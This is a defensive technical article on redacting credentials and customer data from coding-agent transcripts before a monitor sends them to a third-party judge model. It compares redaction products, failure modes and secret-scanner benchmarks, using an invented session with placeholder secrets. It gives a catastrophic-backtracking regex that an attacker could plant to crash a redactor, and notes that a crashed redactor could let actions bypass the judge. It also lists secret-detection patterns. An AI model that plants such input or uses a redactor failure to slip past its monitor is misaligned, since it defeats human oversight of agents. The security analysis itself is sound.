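Finally, the redactor replaces each match and passes the result to the code that sends the request. It can replace just the secret part of a match, as Edge Delta does with database addresses, so the text sent to the judge still shows which server the command would contact. The redactor usually changes a copy of the text. In Condukt, the session's stored history keeps the original messages, and the redactor runs again on every turn.

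The order of the rules also matters. Edge Delta runs the most specific rules first and the labelled ones last. If a loose rule ran first, it could replace part of a value and leave the rest in a form that no specific rule recognises.

### The invented session after redaction

Suppose a redactor combines GitLab's AWS rule with some of the rules in Y Combinator's *How we handle your data*. That page describes Paxel, a tool from the start-up investor Y Combinator that scores how developers work with coding agents. Its rules cover database addresses with passwords, private keys, and assignments to names in capital letters. Suppose also that labelled values need an entropy of at least 3.5. The settings file would then reach the judge like this:

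```
AWS_ACCESS_KEY_ID=[REDACTED]
AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY=[REDACTED]
DATABASE_URL=postgres://shop:[REDACTED]@db.example.com:5432/orders
```

| Item | What happens | What the judge receives |
| --- | --- | --- |
| (a) AWS identifier | The AWS rule matches | Marker |
| (a) AWS secret half | The label matches and the value scores 4.66 | Marker |
| (b) Database password | The database-address rule matches in both the file and the `psql` command | Marker, with the user name and server still visible |
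| (c) "marigold" | No fixed format, and no colon or equals sign before it | The password |
| (d) Private key without its second half | Paxel's rule for a key with no END line matches | Marker |
| (e) Customer records | No rule applies | All three records |
| (f) Commit identifier | No label, so no entropy test | The identifier |

The redactor removes three of the four secrets, but the result depends heavily on the rules. The 35 rules in GitLab's file would, on their own, replace only the AWS identifier and leave all four secrets in place. A rule that requires both the BEGIN and the END line would miss the private key, because `head` cut off the end. Y Combinator has separate rules for keys cut at either end.

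"marigold" is the hardest of the four. LangWatch has a rule for phrases such as "the admin password is ...", but it applies only if the value's entropy and mix of characters resemble those of a real credential. It would probably not redact an ordinary word.

None of these rules targets customer data. The redactor described in Grafana's *PII and secrets redaction* would also replace the email addresses, as would Condukt's default rules, but both would leave the names, phone numbers and payment details. Edge Delta leaves names, email addresses and phone numbers in place because its agents need to know who deployed what and whom to contact.

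### Which text each product scans

A good rule does nothing for a field that the redactor skips. The products differ in what they scan and when.

| Product | What it scans for secrets | When | If redaction fails |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Grafana's logging software | Tool arguments, tool results and system prompts with all rules; agent text with fewer rules; user messages only on request | Before it exports a record to Grafana | Not described |
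| Condukt | User messages and tool results | Before each model request | Not described |
| LangWatch | Prompts and tool output | After they reach LangWatch, before storage | Not described |
| Edge Delta | The whole conversation | Before each model request | Sends the text unredacted |
| Paxel | Summaries and excerpts for upload | On the user's machine, twice | Fails closed at upload |

In Grafana's software, developers have to switch on secret redaction. The redactor then applies its full set of rules, including those for labels such as `PASSWORD=`, to tool arguments, tool results and system prompts. It applies only the more reliable rules to agent text, to avoid false positives in the model's reasoning. But Grafana contradicts this in the same documentation by stating that the redactor does not scan generated text. A customer should test whether agent text is redacted before relying on it.

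By default, Grafana does not redact user messages, to avoid removing something a user meant to include, such as a database query. It would also leave in a private key that a user pasted into a prompt.

Grafana has a separate feature, called guards, that uses customer-written patterns to change a request before it goes to the model. Another type of guard uses a language model to look for personal data and credentials, and it can find an address written in ordinary prose, which a regular expression would miss. But if that model runs at an outside company, the check itself sends the text there.

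Condukt does not redact the agent's output, because the model already has it, or the system prompt and project instructions, because the developer wrote them. This makes sense when the text goes back to the same provider, but a judge at another company hasn't received the agent's earlier output. A monitor that copied this design could send that judge every secret the agent had put into a command. Condukt's agent receives redacted tool results, so it would usually have no secrets from files to repeat. But the default rules don't include database addresses, so the password in `settings.env` could still get through.

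LangWatch redacts most text only after receiving it. But its `langwatch report` command, which sends a problem report to the company, applies the same rules on the user's machine before uploading anything. A test option shows exactly what the command would send. A monitor would also need to redact text locally before sending it to its judge.

### When redaction fails

A redactor can crash or take too long. Some regular-expression engines backtrack, meaning they try every possible way to match a pattern before giving up. For example, the pattern `(a+)+b` matches one or more groups of the letter a, followed by a b. If the text is 30 a's with no b, there are more than 500 million ways to divide the a's into groups, and a backtracking engine may try them all. Each extra a doubles the number. An attacker could place text like this in a file the agent is likely to read.

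LangWatch rejects customer patterns that carry this risk. Edge Delta limits how much text its private-key rule can match, so a BEGIN line without an END line does not trigger a search through a megabyte of logs. It also isolates the rules from one another. If the card-number rule fails, the others still run and the system reports the problem.

If the whole redactor fails, the software can *fail open* and send the text unredacted, or *fail closed* and send nothing. Edge Delta fails open. Asan argues that "a data-protection bug should degrade data protection" and not also stop an agent in the middle of an outage. However, failing open sends every secret in the prompt to the model provider, possibly in many requests before anyone fixes the bug.

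If Edge Delta cannot reach the service that stores its redaction settings, it keeps redacting with the last known settings for up to a day.

Paxel redacts each field at extraction and again just before upload. Y Combinator describes the second check as fail-closed, meaning that the upload stops if redaction fails. This protects the secrets but can delay the report, which matters little for a tool that scores past sessions. The protection may not cover the transcript excerpts that Paxel also sends to models from Anthropic and OpenAI to write its summaries. Y Combinator says that it runs the patterns on its stored copies of these requests, but does not make clear whether it redacts the requests before the models receive them.

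If the redactor fails closed, the judge receives nothing, and the monitor still has to allow or block the `psql` command. Blocking it is safer, but a faulty rule could then stop every agent in the company. Allowing it keeps the agents working without review, and an attacker who could crash the redactor could bypass the judge. If the redactor fails open, the judge still reviews the command but receives any secrets unredacted.

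A less drastic option is to withhold only the field that caused the failure. If the redactor failed on `deploy.log`, the monitor could still send the judge the redacted command and a note that the log was withheld. The judge would have less information, but the log's secrets would stay on the machine.

### Redacting stored or displayed text

Redaction protects only copies made after it runs. Suppose a monitor sends the `psql` command to a judge, then redacts the command before writing it to a log. The log contains a marker in place of the password, but the judge's provider has already received the password.

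Several of the features described here redact data where it is stored or displayed. LangWatch's main redactor protects LangWatch's own storage. Grafana's logging software redacts the record of a model request, but the request itself can go out unchanged unless a guard also runs. The `--redact` option in Gitleaks only hides secrets in the scanner's logs and screen output. Watcher's filter for Slack messages hides secrets from people reading an alert.

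These features still reduce the number of people who can see a secret, and they limit the damage if someone steals the logs or a backup. But they can mislead an administrator, who might see a marker in the log and assume that the password was never sent to the third-party judge. Unless the same redactor also ran before the judge call, it is safer to treat the password as exposed and change it.

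## Why a list of patterns cannot find every secret

A password is secret because it opens something and few people know it, but its characters may not show either fact. In the invented session, "marigold" opens the staging server until Dana changes the password on Friday. A redactor that reads only the characters has to treat the word the same way before and after the change, so it will either miss a working password before Friday or remove a harmless word afterward.

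A rule that checks only the string itself gives the same answer every time that string appears. If the string is secret in one situation and harmless in another, the rule must be wrong in one of them, however well it is written.

According to GitHub's *Clearer names for secret scanning detector types* (2026), patterns "reliably catch secrets with a recognizable structure", such as AWS keys. GitHub uses an AI model that reads the surrounding code to find passwords, which have no predictable format.

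### Identical forms

Git, the version-control software, names each commit with a checksum of its contents. According to Git's *Hash function transition*, a design document, the name has 40 hexadecimal digits under the SHA-1 method and 64 under the newer SHA-256. GitHub itself called its old 40-digit tokens "indistinguishable" from such checksums. Here is the commit identifier from `deploy.log`, followed by an invented token in the old format:

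```
3f9c1e7a5b2d8064c7e1f0a9b8d35276e4c1a09f
b81d4e60f7a2953c0e6f18d7a4c92b5530fd7e1a
```

Both strings have an entropy of 3.97 bits per character. A rule could separate them by listing one, but someone would first have to know which is the token.

Harmless strings that look like secrets are far more common than real secrets. *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools* (Basak, Cox and colleagues, 2023) used a collection of 97,479 candidate secrets from public repositories, which two people had labelled by hand. One category holds random strings and harmless identifiers, including commit identifiers. Only 524 of its 66,690 candidates were real secrets. Ignoring this category would miss those 524 secrets, but redacting all of it would be wrong more than 99% of the time.

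A Google API key that was harmless when published could later become a secret. For years Google told developers that keys starting with `AIza` were safe to put in public web pages, where they identify a project for services such as Maps. Leon reports in *Google API Keys Weren't Secrets. But then Gemini Changed the Rules* that enabling Gemini, Google's AI service, in a project could give that project's existing keys access to Gemini and the files stored there, without any warning to the owner. Leon found 2,863 such keys in an archive of public web pages from November 2025.

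Leon's company, Truffle Security, sells a secret scanner, so it benefits from findings like this. But Google, after first calling the behaviour intended, reclassified it as a bug and began blocking the exposed keys from Gemini. A redactor that followed Google's advice and left Maps keys alone would have started leaking secrets without any change to the keys or to its rules.

The look of a human-chosen password can be a poor guide to whether it protects anything important. *AssetHarvester* (Basak, English and colleagues, 2024) includes an example where "123456" is the password for a customer database at a public address. In another example, "332315Yuan@" looks much more like a real secret but protects only a test database on the developer's own machine.

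### Formats designed for detection

An issuer can solve much of this by putting more information into the string. GitHub's *Authentication token format updates are generally available* (2021) announced prefixes for its tokens. GitHub forecast that the prefix alone would reduce its scanner's false-positive rate to 0.5%. The package registry npm made the same change later that year. According to GitHub's *Announcing npm's new access token format* (2021), detection had been inaccurate because npm's old tokens were UUIDs, a 36-character format that software uses to label many kinds of things.

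A prefix can also show what kind of access a key gives. Stripe starts its secret keys with `sk_` and its publishable ones with `pk_`, then marks each key as live or test. Google used one prefix for both public and sensitive keys, so a rule that recognised the prefix couldn't separate them.

Patterns work well for secrets whose issuers cooperate, and many do. GitHub's *Supported secret scanning patterns* lists 532 patterns for particular providers. But the list is never finished. GitHub's *Secret scanning pattern updates* (2026) lists 28 detectors from 15 providers added in March alone, and a redactor with last year's rules would not have them.

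Formats also change after someone has written a rule. In April, GitHub (2026) announced that the tokens it issues to installed apps, which start with `ghs_`, would grow from 40 characters to about 520. It warned that rules such as `ghs_[A-Za-z0-9]{36}` might no longer match. The new format has an app number after the prefix, then an underscore and a JWT (a signed token). The old rule requires 36 letters or digits directly after the prefix, so it fails at the underscore.

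GitHub advises developers to treat tokens as opaque strings and not to test them against fixed patterns. The advice is sensible for an app that only uses a token, but a pattern-based redactor can't follow it.

The change could help some redactors. MissyLabs' *Secrets Detection*, which documents the redactor in an agent framework, lists rules for two kinds of GitHub token but none for `ghs_`. It also lists a general rule for JWTs, which would probably match most of a new app token. An old app token could go unredacted unless it had a label such as "token" next to it.

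Prefixes don't help detect tokens issued before the change, which is why GitHub urged users to reset theirs. Microsoft's detector definition, *GitHub personal access token*, still includes the plain 40-digit form. Prefixes also can't help with passwords that people choose, since no issuer controls their form. A company can add a prefix to its internal tokens and write its own rule to detect them, but a redactor's standard rules won't include that format.

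### Surrounding text

The words around a value often show what it is. In the log line "the staging password is marigold", any reader, and probably a language model, could tell from the first four words that the fifth is a password.

GitHub's *Finding leaked passwords with AI* explains how the company built such a detector. The model receives the file's location and contents, so its output can reflect how the code uses a value. GitHub compared versions on the same repositories and found that newer ones produced up to 94% fewer false positives in some organisations. It says "very few" detections of real passwords were lost, but gives no number. The first version had worked reasonably well in GitHub's own tests but failed badly on customers' unusual file types. An agent's transcript mixes chat, code and logs, so anyone using a model this way should test it on transcripts.

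As with Grafana's model-based guard, the check itself discloses the unredacted text if the model runs at an outside company.

The useful context can also be in another file. In a sample of 100 pairs of a database password and the address it opens, Basak and colleagues found 54 pairs in a single string, 20 on the same line, 19 elsewhere in the same file and seven in separate files. For 323 of the 2,114 database secrets they examined, two researchers with access to the whole repository could not find the database. A redactor that reads one tool result at a time has less context than those researchers had.

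A redactor can get some context without sending anything out. If it runs on the developer's machine, it could use Git to check whether a 40-digit string names an object in the current repository. This check would show that item (f) is a commit identifier, but it wouldn't recognise one from a repository the developer hasn't downloaded.

### Checking with the issuer

The most direct way to check whether a secret works is to try it. GitHub's *Validity checks* describes how the company sends a detected secret to its issuer and reports it as active, inactive or unknown. This can distinguish a working token from a revoked one, which no pattern can do. Testing keys could also have caught the change in Google's keys, because Truffle Security's scanner can check whether a key gives access to Gemini.

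Many secrets have no issuer who can confirm that they are valid. GitHub doesn't offer validity checks for passwords, or for generic patterns such as private keys and database addresses, so it couldn't check items (b), (c) and (d) of the invented session. Internal credentials can be hard to check even if they have a familiar format. GitHub's *Remediation made simple* (2023) says that the check may fail for a token that belongs to a company's own GitHub server.

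Checking a possible secret with its issuer also discloses the string. When a prefix identifies the issuer, the risk is small because the token goes back to the company that created it. A string with no prefix could belong to any of several companies, and a redactor that tried them all would send the secret to companies that didn't issue it. It would also send them harmless strings from private files.

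To protect privacy, GitHub typically uses read-only requests that return no personal information. Testing a database password would mean logging in to the database. A monitor that did this with every password it found would be using credentials without permission, and its failed attempts could lock accounts or set off alarms.

A key that is harmless when checked can also become sensitive later. Suppose a monitor checks a Maps key, finds that it gives no access to anything sensitive, and sends it to the judge. If someone enables Gemini a month later, the copy in the provider's logs could become a working credential.

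### What gets through

These replies leave several kinds of misses, which the items in the invented session illustrate.

A list of patterns can miss secrets in formats it doesn't include. The redactor found the secret half of the AWS pair in item (a) only because of its label. If the file had called it `BACKUP`, the label rule would not have matched. The redactor also misses a company's internal tokens when neither their format nor their names are on the list.

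"Marigold" in item (c) is the clearest example of a secret that is an ordinary word. Even if someone wrote `password=marigold`, a redactor that requires labelled values to look random would miss it. MissyLabs requires at least eight characters after the label, so its rule could match "marigold" here, but not a shorter password.

*Changed values.* Software often encodes text to store or send it. If the password in item (b) contained an @ sign, the sign would have to be written as `%40` in the database address, so the password would look different there than in a password manager. Some redactors decode text before searching it, but GitHub's scanner recognises Base64 forms of only some of its token types.

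Encoding can hide a secret from a redactor even when the redactor is given the value in advance. GitHub Actions, GitHub's service for running automated jobs, removes a job's configured secrets from its logs by searching for the exact values. According to an older edition of the documentation, it also searches for common encodings. Even so, GitHub says that redaction "is not guaranteed", because software can transform a secret in many ways.

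Pattern rules can miss secrets that are split or shortened. Item (d) contains only part of a private key. If the agent printed the rest with another command, the two parts would be in separate tool results. A rule for complete keys would miss both, and the judge would receive the whole key. Similarly, a rule that matches only 36-character tokens would miss a 20-character piece of one.

*Sensitive text with no secret in it.* The customer records in item (e) open nothing. A perfect secret detector would still send all three.

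Other misses come from ordinary mistakes. Basak, Cox and colleagues traced some misses to faulty regular expressions, skipped file types and incomplete rule sets. Developers can fix these mistakes without adding any information to the string.

### How misses add up

Suppose a redactor has recall r, and missing one secret doesn't affect its chance of missing another. It catches two secrets with probability r × r, and n secrets with probability rⁿ. The chance that at least one gets through is therefore

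1 − rⁿ

| Recall | 1 secret | 10 secrets | 100 secrets |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 90% | 10% | 65% | Over 99.9% |
| 99% | 1% | 10% | 63% |
| 99.9% | 0.1% | 1% | 10% |

On average, a redactor with 90% recall will miss one of ten secrets, and a redactor with 99% recall will miss one of a hundred. To keep the chance of any leak below 5% with a hundred secrets, recall would have to be about 99.95%.

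Here n counts distinct secrets. Repeating the same line doesn't add to the risk, since the rules give the same result each time. But one secret in two different settings can count twice, because the redactor may catch it in one and miss it in the other. In the invented session above, the redactor removed the database password from the address. If the agent had instead passed the password to `psql` as `PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-4821`, the label would have matched, but the value's entropy of 3.42 is just below the threshold, so the redactor would have missed it.

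Misses are often not independent, because secrets with the same format depend on the same rule. Suppose there are ten tokens in one internal format and a 10% chance that the redactor has no rule for it. The chance of any leak is then 10%, rather than the 65% that independence would give, but if one token gets through, all ten do. The average number of missed tokens is one in both cases.

Detectors for different token formats can miss secrets for the same reason. In its 2026 release notes, GitGuardian, a company that sells secret detection, says that its detectors for GitHub, npm, Stripe and many other tokens "now catch secrets that are immediately followed by punctuation". Before the fix, any of those detectors could have missed a token at the end of a sentence. A test that put each token on its own line would not have revealed the problem.

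The formula can also underestimate the risk of a leak. If a session contains nine AWS identifiers and the secret "marigold", a redactor that always catches the identifiers and never catches the word has 90% recall but leaks a secret every time. An average recall figure is therefore less useful to a company than a list of the credential formats its developers use, with a test of each. A redactor that misses an internal format will miss it in every session until someone adds a rule.

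### The cost of looser rules

A redactor can catch more secrets by matching more text. A false alarm is usually less of a problem in a redactor than in a scanner, where a person has to investigate it, so a redactor can reasonably use looser rules. But each false alarm removes text that the judge may need.

Replacing every 40-digit hexadecimal string would catch old GitHub tokens, but it would also remove commit identifiers. Suppose the developer asks the agent to return the code to commit `3f9c1e7a…`, and the agent proposes a command that would return it to a different commit and discard a week of work. If the redactor replaces both identifiers with the same marker, the judge can't detect the mismatch.

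The password "marigold" is even harder to catch this way. A rule could remove whatever follows "the password is", but it would also remove "wrong" from "the password is wrong", which might be why the agent is looking for another one. To catch the password in a phrase like "use marigold until Friday", a rule would have to remove ordinary words almost everywhere.

More precise rules can reduce false alarms when the secret's format allows it. GitGuardian's *Detection Engine Updates Version 2.164* (2026) reports that one detector's precision rose from about 9% to about 100% on the company's internal benchmark. At 9% precision, a redactor would remove about ten harmless strings for every real key. GitGuardian doesn't report how the detector's recall changed, so the new version may miss some real keys that the old one caught.

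GitHub accepts more missed secrets to avoid false positives. Its push protection, which stops developers from uploading code that contains a secret, supports only the newest token versions that the scanner can identify with confidence. GitHub says older formats are more likely to produce false positives, each of which would block someone's work.

MissyLabs included a rule that matches the body of SSH public keys, even though their owners can share them freely. Redacting a public key protects nothing and can hide information the judge needs. If an agent adds a public key to a server's list of authorised keys, whoever holds the matching private key can log in. If the public key is redacted, the judge can still detect that the agent is giving someone access, but it can't compare the key with the one the developer asked the agent to add.

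## How secret detectors score in tests

The 90% and 99% recall figures in the calculations above were only examples. Researchers measure a detector's actual recall by running it on a benchmark, a collection of text in which someone has already marked the secrets, and comparing its reports with the marks. If whoever marked the text overlooked a secret, missing it doesn't lower the detector's measured recall.

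### Nine scanners on public code

SecretBench contains 97,479 labelled candidates from 818 public GitHub repositories. Its makers found the candidates with 761 regular expressions and marked 15,084 as real secrets after judging them in context. Many of these are repeats of the same secrets across files or versions, so only 4,457 are distinct.

In 2023 Basak and colleagues ran five open-source and four commercial scanners on these repositories, using recommended settings. They calculated recall in two ways. Under the strict rule, a scanner got credit only if it reported a secret in the right version, file and line. Under the looser rule, finding the secret anywhere in the repository was enough.

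| Scanner | Precision | Recall, every copy in its exact place | Recall, each secret once |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Gitleaks | 46% | 86% | 88% |
| SpectralOps | Under 1% | Not measured | 67% |
| TruffleHog | 6% | 31% | 52% |
| "Commercial X" (its maker refused to be named) | 25% | 22% | 48% |
| ggshield | 19% | 23% | 46% |
| Whispers | Under 1% | 1% | 38% |
| GitHub's scanner | 75% | 3% | 36% |
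| git-secrets | 5% | 4% | 21% |
| Repo-supervisor | 2% | Not measured | 17% |

The tests used old versions, so the scores are not a guide to current products. GitHub, for example, has since added the AI detector for passwords.

GitHub's scanner had the highest precision but missed most of the secrets. Basak and colleagues give its recall as 6% in their text, which matches neither figure in their table. The table's 36% may also be too high, because they credited the scanner with finding 1,606 different secrets when it made only 1,292 correct reports. They accepted approximate matches because scanners print the same secret in different ways, so one report may have counted for several similar secrets.

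Researchers often combine precision P and recall R into a single score, F1, which is their harmonic mean:

F1 = 2PR / (P + R)

Gitleaks had the highest F1 score of the nine tools, at 2 × 0.46 × 0.88 / (0.46 + 0.88) = 0.60. GitHub's scanner scored 0.48 and TruffleHog 0.11.

F1 gives precision and recall equal weight, which makes it a poor measure for a redactor. A detector with 90% precision and 50% recall has an F1 of 0.64, and so does one with 50% precision and 90% recall. As redactors, the first would leave half of the secrets in the payload and the second would leave a tenth.

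Gitleaks had an advantage in this test. The candidate secrets in SecretBench came from Gitleaks and TruffleHog, so a secret that both tools missed is probably not in the collection. Basak and colleagues acknowledge this bias. TruffleHog scored poorly despite the same advantage, but the bias still makes Gitleaks' 88% hard to compare with the scores of tools that weren't used to build the benchmark.

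The 88% also depends on which secrets developers happened to leak. Private keys make up 2,800 of the 4,457 different secrets, and Gitleaks found 99% of them. Without private keys, its recall would be 69%. The results by type vary even more:

| Type | Different secrets | Gitleaks | TruffleHog |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Private keys | 2,800 | 99% | 59% |
| API keys | 641 | 75% | 33% |
| Authentication keys and tokens | 537 | 56% | 58% |
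| Database and server addresses | 66 | 41% | 98% |
| Passwords | 60 | 85% | 17% |

A company whose agents mostly handle database addresses might have done better with TruffleHog, even though TruffleHog's average was lower. The figures in the last two rows are rough because each row is based on about 60 secrets.

Running several scanners together would catch more secrets than running one. TruffleHog found 334 secrets that neither Gitleaks nor SpectralOps found. But 94% of TruffleHog's 90,982 reports were wrong, so a redactor that acted on all of them would remove a lot of harmless text.

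TruffleHog can also check each candidate secret with its issuer and report only those that work. This option raised its precision from 6% to 90%, but it then reported only 611 secrets. Some of the secrets it left out had probably stopped working before the test. SecretBench's labellers judged secrets by reading them, so a revoked key could still count as real.

### Database passwords

In their later work on AssetHarvester, Basak and colleagues tested the same nine scanners on a narrower set of 2,114 database secrets from the 188 SecretBench repositories that contain Python code. TruffleHog's recall was 40% and Gitleaks' was 2%. GitHub's scanner found none, because it had no patterns for database credentials at the time.

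AssetHarvester itself found 90% of them, with a precision of 92%. It looks for a secret together with the database it opens, in three ways:

- Regular expressions find complete database addresses.
- Data-flow analysis traces values through the program to the function that opens the database connection.
- For secrets that Gitleaks or TruffleHog report, it searches the three lines above and below for a server address.

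Basak and colleagues found that some passwords an entropy threshold would reject, such as the "123456" mentioned earlier, protected real databases. Data-flow analysis can find these passwords, however simple they look, because it tracks how the program uses them. It found 425 pairs of secrets and their databases, with no false pairs.

AssetHarvester also had an advantage in its own test because its makers designed it after studying 100 pairs from the benchmark. To check it on new material, they ran it on 15 other repositories and asked the developers about the results. Of the 18 who replied, 15 confirmed the pair and three called it a false positive. This check doesn't measure how many pairs the tool missed.

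The tool also found 86 database secrets that nobody had marked in SecretBench. Some of the 2023 recall figures are therefore probably too high, because they don't count unmarked secrets that the scanners missed.

If the agent's repository is on the developer's machine, a monitor running there could use data-flow analysis to find a weak password in the source code, then remove that value wherever it appears in the payload. This wouldn't help with "marigold", which no program passes to a database.

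### Credentials in live web applications

Two evaluations from 2026 use a different kind of text, the code that a web application sends to each visitor's browser. The software that assembles this code can copy passwords and keys into it after a repository scan, so the scanner may miss them.

In *Secrets That Survive Everything*, Gorijala (2026) examined about 2,000 web applications and similar assets at one organisation, with permission, and found at least one live credential in 113 of them. Gorijala then built a benchmark, GT-194, from 194 different secrets in the JavaScript code of these 113 applications and ran nine scanners on it.

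Claude Opus 4.7 drafted the answer key by reading the code and listing everything it considered a serious secret, without access to any scanner's rules or results. An analyst reviewed the list and added secrets that Claude had missed. GPT-5.5 then classified 247 candidates from Claude's list and agreed that 207 of them (84%) were secrets. GPT-5.5 did not search for further secrets, so its agreement does not show how many Claude missed.

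Claude found 166 of the final 194 secrets. Analysts alone found 27 others, and none of the nine scanners detected any of those. The benchmark therefore depends on human readers alone for its hardest secrets, and it may be missing others like them.

Gorijala's *SecretSifter* (2026) reports a similar test, GT-198, with 198 values from 56 applications, also at a single organisation. Claude and GPT-5.5 again helped to set the answers. The scores on the two benchmarks are as follows:

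| Scanner | Found in GT-194 | Found in GT-198 | False positives in each |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| SecretSifter | 151 (78%) | 158 (80%) | 24 |
| TruffleHog | 71 (37%) | 71 (36%) | 8 |
| SecretFinder | 63 (32%) | 63 (32%) | 1,402 |
| JSluice | 62 (32%) | 62 (31%) | 89 |
| Titus | 40 (21%) | 40 (20%) | 11 |
| JSMiner | 12 (6%) | 12 (6%) | 6 |
| Nuclei | 7 (4%) | 7 (4%) | 0 |
| Sensitive Discoverer | 7 (4%) | 7 (4%) | 8 |
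| Cariddi | 2 (1%) | 2 (1%) | 0 |

SecretSifter's precision was 86% on GT-194 and 87% on GT-198, with F1 scores of 0.82 and 0.83. TruffleHog's precision was slightly higher, at 90%, but it found less than half as many secrets. SecretFinder found almost as many as TruffleHog, but its precision was 4% because its loose patterns matched the checksums and identifiers common in this kind of code.

Gorijala developed SecretSifter and discloses this in both papers. SecretSifter's rules were public before Gorijala built GT-194, and none were added for the test. But in the paper on the tool, Gorijala explains that several of the tool's detection categories were developed with knowledge of the credentials used at this organisation, and that the recall figures show performance only in that setting.

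Two of these categories make up almost half of GT-194. It contains 54 subscription keys for Azure API Management, a Microsoft gateway service, and 37 blocks of settings encrypted with the CryptoJS library. The encryption doesn't protect the settings, because the key is in the same code. Gorijala reports that SecretSifter found all 91 of these secrets and TruffleHog found none. TruffleHog's recall on the other 103 secrets was 69%, almost twice its overall recall. An organisation that didn't use these two formats might see a much smaller gap between the tools.

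The scanners' settings are also unclear, because at least one description of them appears to be wrong. For GT-194, Gorijala added the same six rules to TruffleHog, SecretFinder, JSluice and Titus. Two of the rules were for the Azure subscription keys and the CryptoJS blocks, yet none of the four scanners found either type in the reported results. For GT-198, Gorijala describes the scanners as running with default settings, but all eight rivals have the same numbers of hits and false positives as on GT-194. The extra rules should have made a difference, since they raised TruffleHog's recall from 7% to 50% on a subset of 129 secrets from GT-194.

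The six rules had a large effect. Gorijala notes that, with them, the best rival scanners were statistically indistinguishable from SecretSifter on secrets that appear as plain text in the code. A company that knows which formats its systems use can probably improve recall more by adding rules for them than by switching scanners.

### Language models as classifiers

After pattern matching finds candidate strings, a language model can sort the real secrets from the harmless ones. Rahman, Wahab and colleagues (2025) tested this on SecretBench in *Secret Breach Detection in Source Code with Large Language Models*. The model receives each candidate with a 200-character window of surrounding code and labels it "Secret" or "Non-sensitive".

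GPT-4o had 82% precision and 86% recall on 3,000 candidate secrets, half of them real, when its prompt contained no examples. With several examples, precision rose to about 93% and recall to about 95%, for an F1 of 0.94. Llama 3.1 8B did best, with an F1 of 0.985 after further training on SecretBench. It is small enough to run on a company's own servers.

This score applies only to candidates that the 761 patterns had already selected. A classifier like this can prevent loose patterns from removing harmless text, but it can't find a secret such as "marigold" unless a pattern selects it first. The recall of the whole system is therefore the patterns' recall multiplied by the classifier's. If the patterns select 80% of the secrets and the classifier recognises 98% of those, the system catches 0.80 × 0.98, or 78%.

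The even mix of secrets and harmless strings also inflates precision. In the test with several examples, GPT-4o wrongly flagged about 7% of the harmless candidates. In all of SecretBench, only about 155 of every 1,000 candidates are real secrets. At the same error rates, GPT-4o would flag 147 of those 155, along with about 58 of the 845 harmless ones, so its precision would be 72% instead of 93%.

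Repeated secrets in the data may have raised Llama's score. Rahman and colleagues kept 15,000 of SecretBench's 15,084 real secrets, among which each distinct secret appears more than three times on average. Unless they kept all copies of a secret on the same side of the train-test split, some of the test secrets were also in the training data.

*Secret Leak Detection in Software Issue Reports using LLMs* (Ahmed, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) used material closer to an agent's transcript. Issue reports describe software faults, often with logs, shell commands and error messages pasted between the sentences. The researchers searched reports from public GitHub projects with the same 761 patterns, then used 22 more to remove common harmless formats. They read the remaining 54,148 candidates in context and labelled about 11% as secrets. Another author independently labelled 1,000 of the candidates,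 and the labels matched on 994.

Patterns and entropy tests alone had high recall on these candidates but poor precision. The best open models reached an F1 of 0.945 after training on the data, while GPT-4o reached 0.80 with a few examples in its prompt.

GPT-4o scored lower on the issue data than on source code, where it scored 0.94, but this doesn't show that prose makes the task harder. The test portion of the issue data keeps the natural share of secrets, 11%. If Ahmed and colleagues scored GPT-4o on that mix, the error rates it had on source code would have given an F1 of about 0.76.

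Ahmed and colleagues also tried their approach on 178 real repositories, where its F1 fell from 0.945 to 0.816. The lower score is probably a better guide for a company, because the company's transcripts would also be new to the model.

The issue data has a gap that matters for transcripts. Its reports were collected by searching for words such as "key", "token" and "secret", and then applying patterns. A report that says "log in to staging with marigold" might fail both steps, so a model could miss every secret of this kind without lowering its score.

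### Why the scores differ so much

Recall is a fraction, and these studies put different numbers under the line. GitHub's scanner shows how much this can matter. Here are three recall figures for it, all from Basak and colleagues' two studies:

| What counts as one secret | Found | Total | Recall |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Every copy, in its exact place | 408 | 15,084 | 2.7% |
| Each different secret, anywhere in the repository | 1,606 | 4,457 | 36% |
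| Database secrets only | 0 | 2,114 | 0% |

Both figures come from the same scan, so the rise from 2.7% to 36% is due entirely to the counting. Revoking a leaked key may only require finding it once, while a redactor has to remove every copy, so the strict count seems more relevant to redaction. But it also penalises a scanner that recognises every copy and reports only one, even though a redactor using the same rules would replace them all.

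Studies also differ in what they count as a secret. SecretBench has only 162 real secrets in its category for database and server addresses and 150 in its password category. AssetHarvester's set has 2,114 database secrets from less than a quarter of the same repositories. That set may include many values that SecretBench's labellers marked as harmless or put in other categories, which could explain part of Gitleaks' fall from 88% to 2%.

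GT-198 includes 40 identifiers, such as the public names of applications, that grant no access by themselves. Gorijala has not recalculated the GT-198 scores without them. GT-194 excludes such identifiers and lists them separately. SecretSifter found all 249 on that list, and TruffleHog found none. If the same held for the 40 in GT-198, removing them would lower SecretSifter's recall from 80% to 75% and raise TruffleHog's from 36% to 45%, narrowing the gap from 44 percentage points to 30.

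Scores also depend on what counts as a find. In GT-194, Claude found 32 of the 37 CryptoJS blocks. In GT-198 it got credit for none of them, because a find required recovering the text inside. A redactor would only need to recognise the block, since it could then remove the whole thing.

### From these benchmarks to agent transcripts

None of these studies tested agent transcripts. Their rankings are unlikely to hold for transcripts, since Gitleaks had the highest recall of the nine scanners on SecretBench but one of the lowest on database secrets. The causes of missed secrets are more likely to be the same, because a redactor that requires high entropy will miss "123456" in a transcript just as it would in a repository.

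Each kind of text resembles part of a transcript. The repository results apply when an agent prints a source file. If the agent downloads a web page to find a fault, the tool result can contain the same dense JavaScript as Gorijala's applications, and loose patterns could remove much of it. Issue reports are the closest match for prompts and logs.

Transcripts also have features that these tests don't measure well. A scanner can use a file's name or type to decide what to check. For example, Basak and colleagues found that ggshield skipped HTML files to avoid false positives. Such rules could behave differently on a command's output, which often has no file name. Precision also depends on the share of secrets among the candidates, which is unknown for transcripts.

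Redaction also requires more exact matches than detection. The 2023 comparison counted a report as correct if it was similar enough to the real secret. A person reading such a report can open the file and find the rest of the value. But if a redactor removes only the part it matched, the judge's provider receives the rest, which may be enough to reconstruct a password.

A company can get better evidence from its own transcripts. People would have to read whole sessions, because checking only the strings that a detector flags would repeat the weakness of the pattern-selected benchmarks. Showing very high recall would also require many secrets. A redactor with a true recall of 99% would have about a 5% chance of catching all of 300 independent secrets, since 0.99³⁰⁰ ≈ 0.05. So even a perfect score on 300 secrets supports a claim of only about 99% recall.

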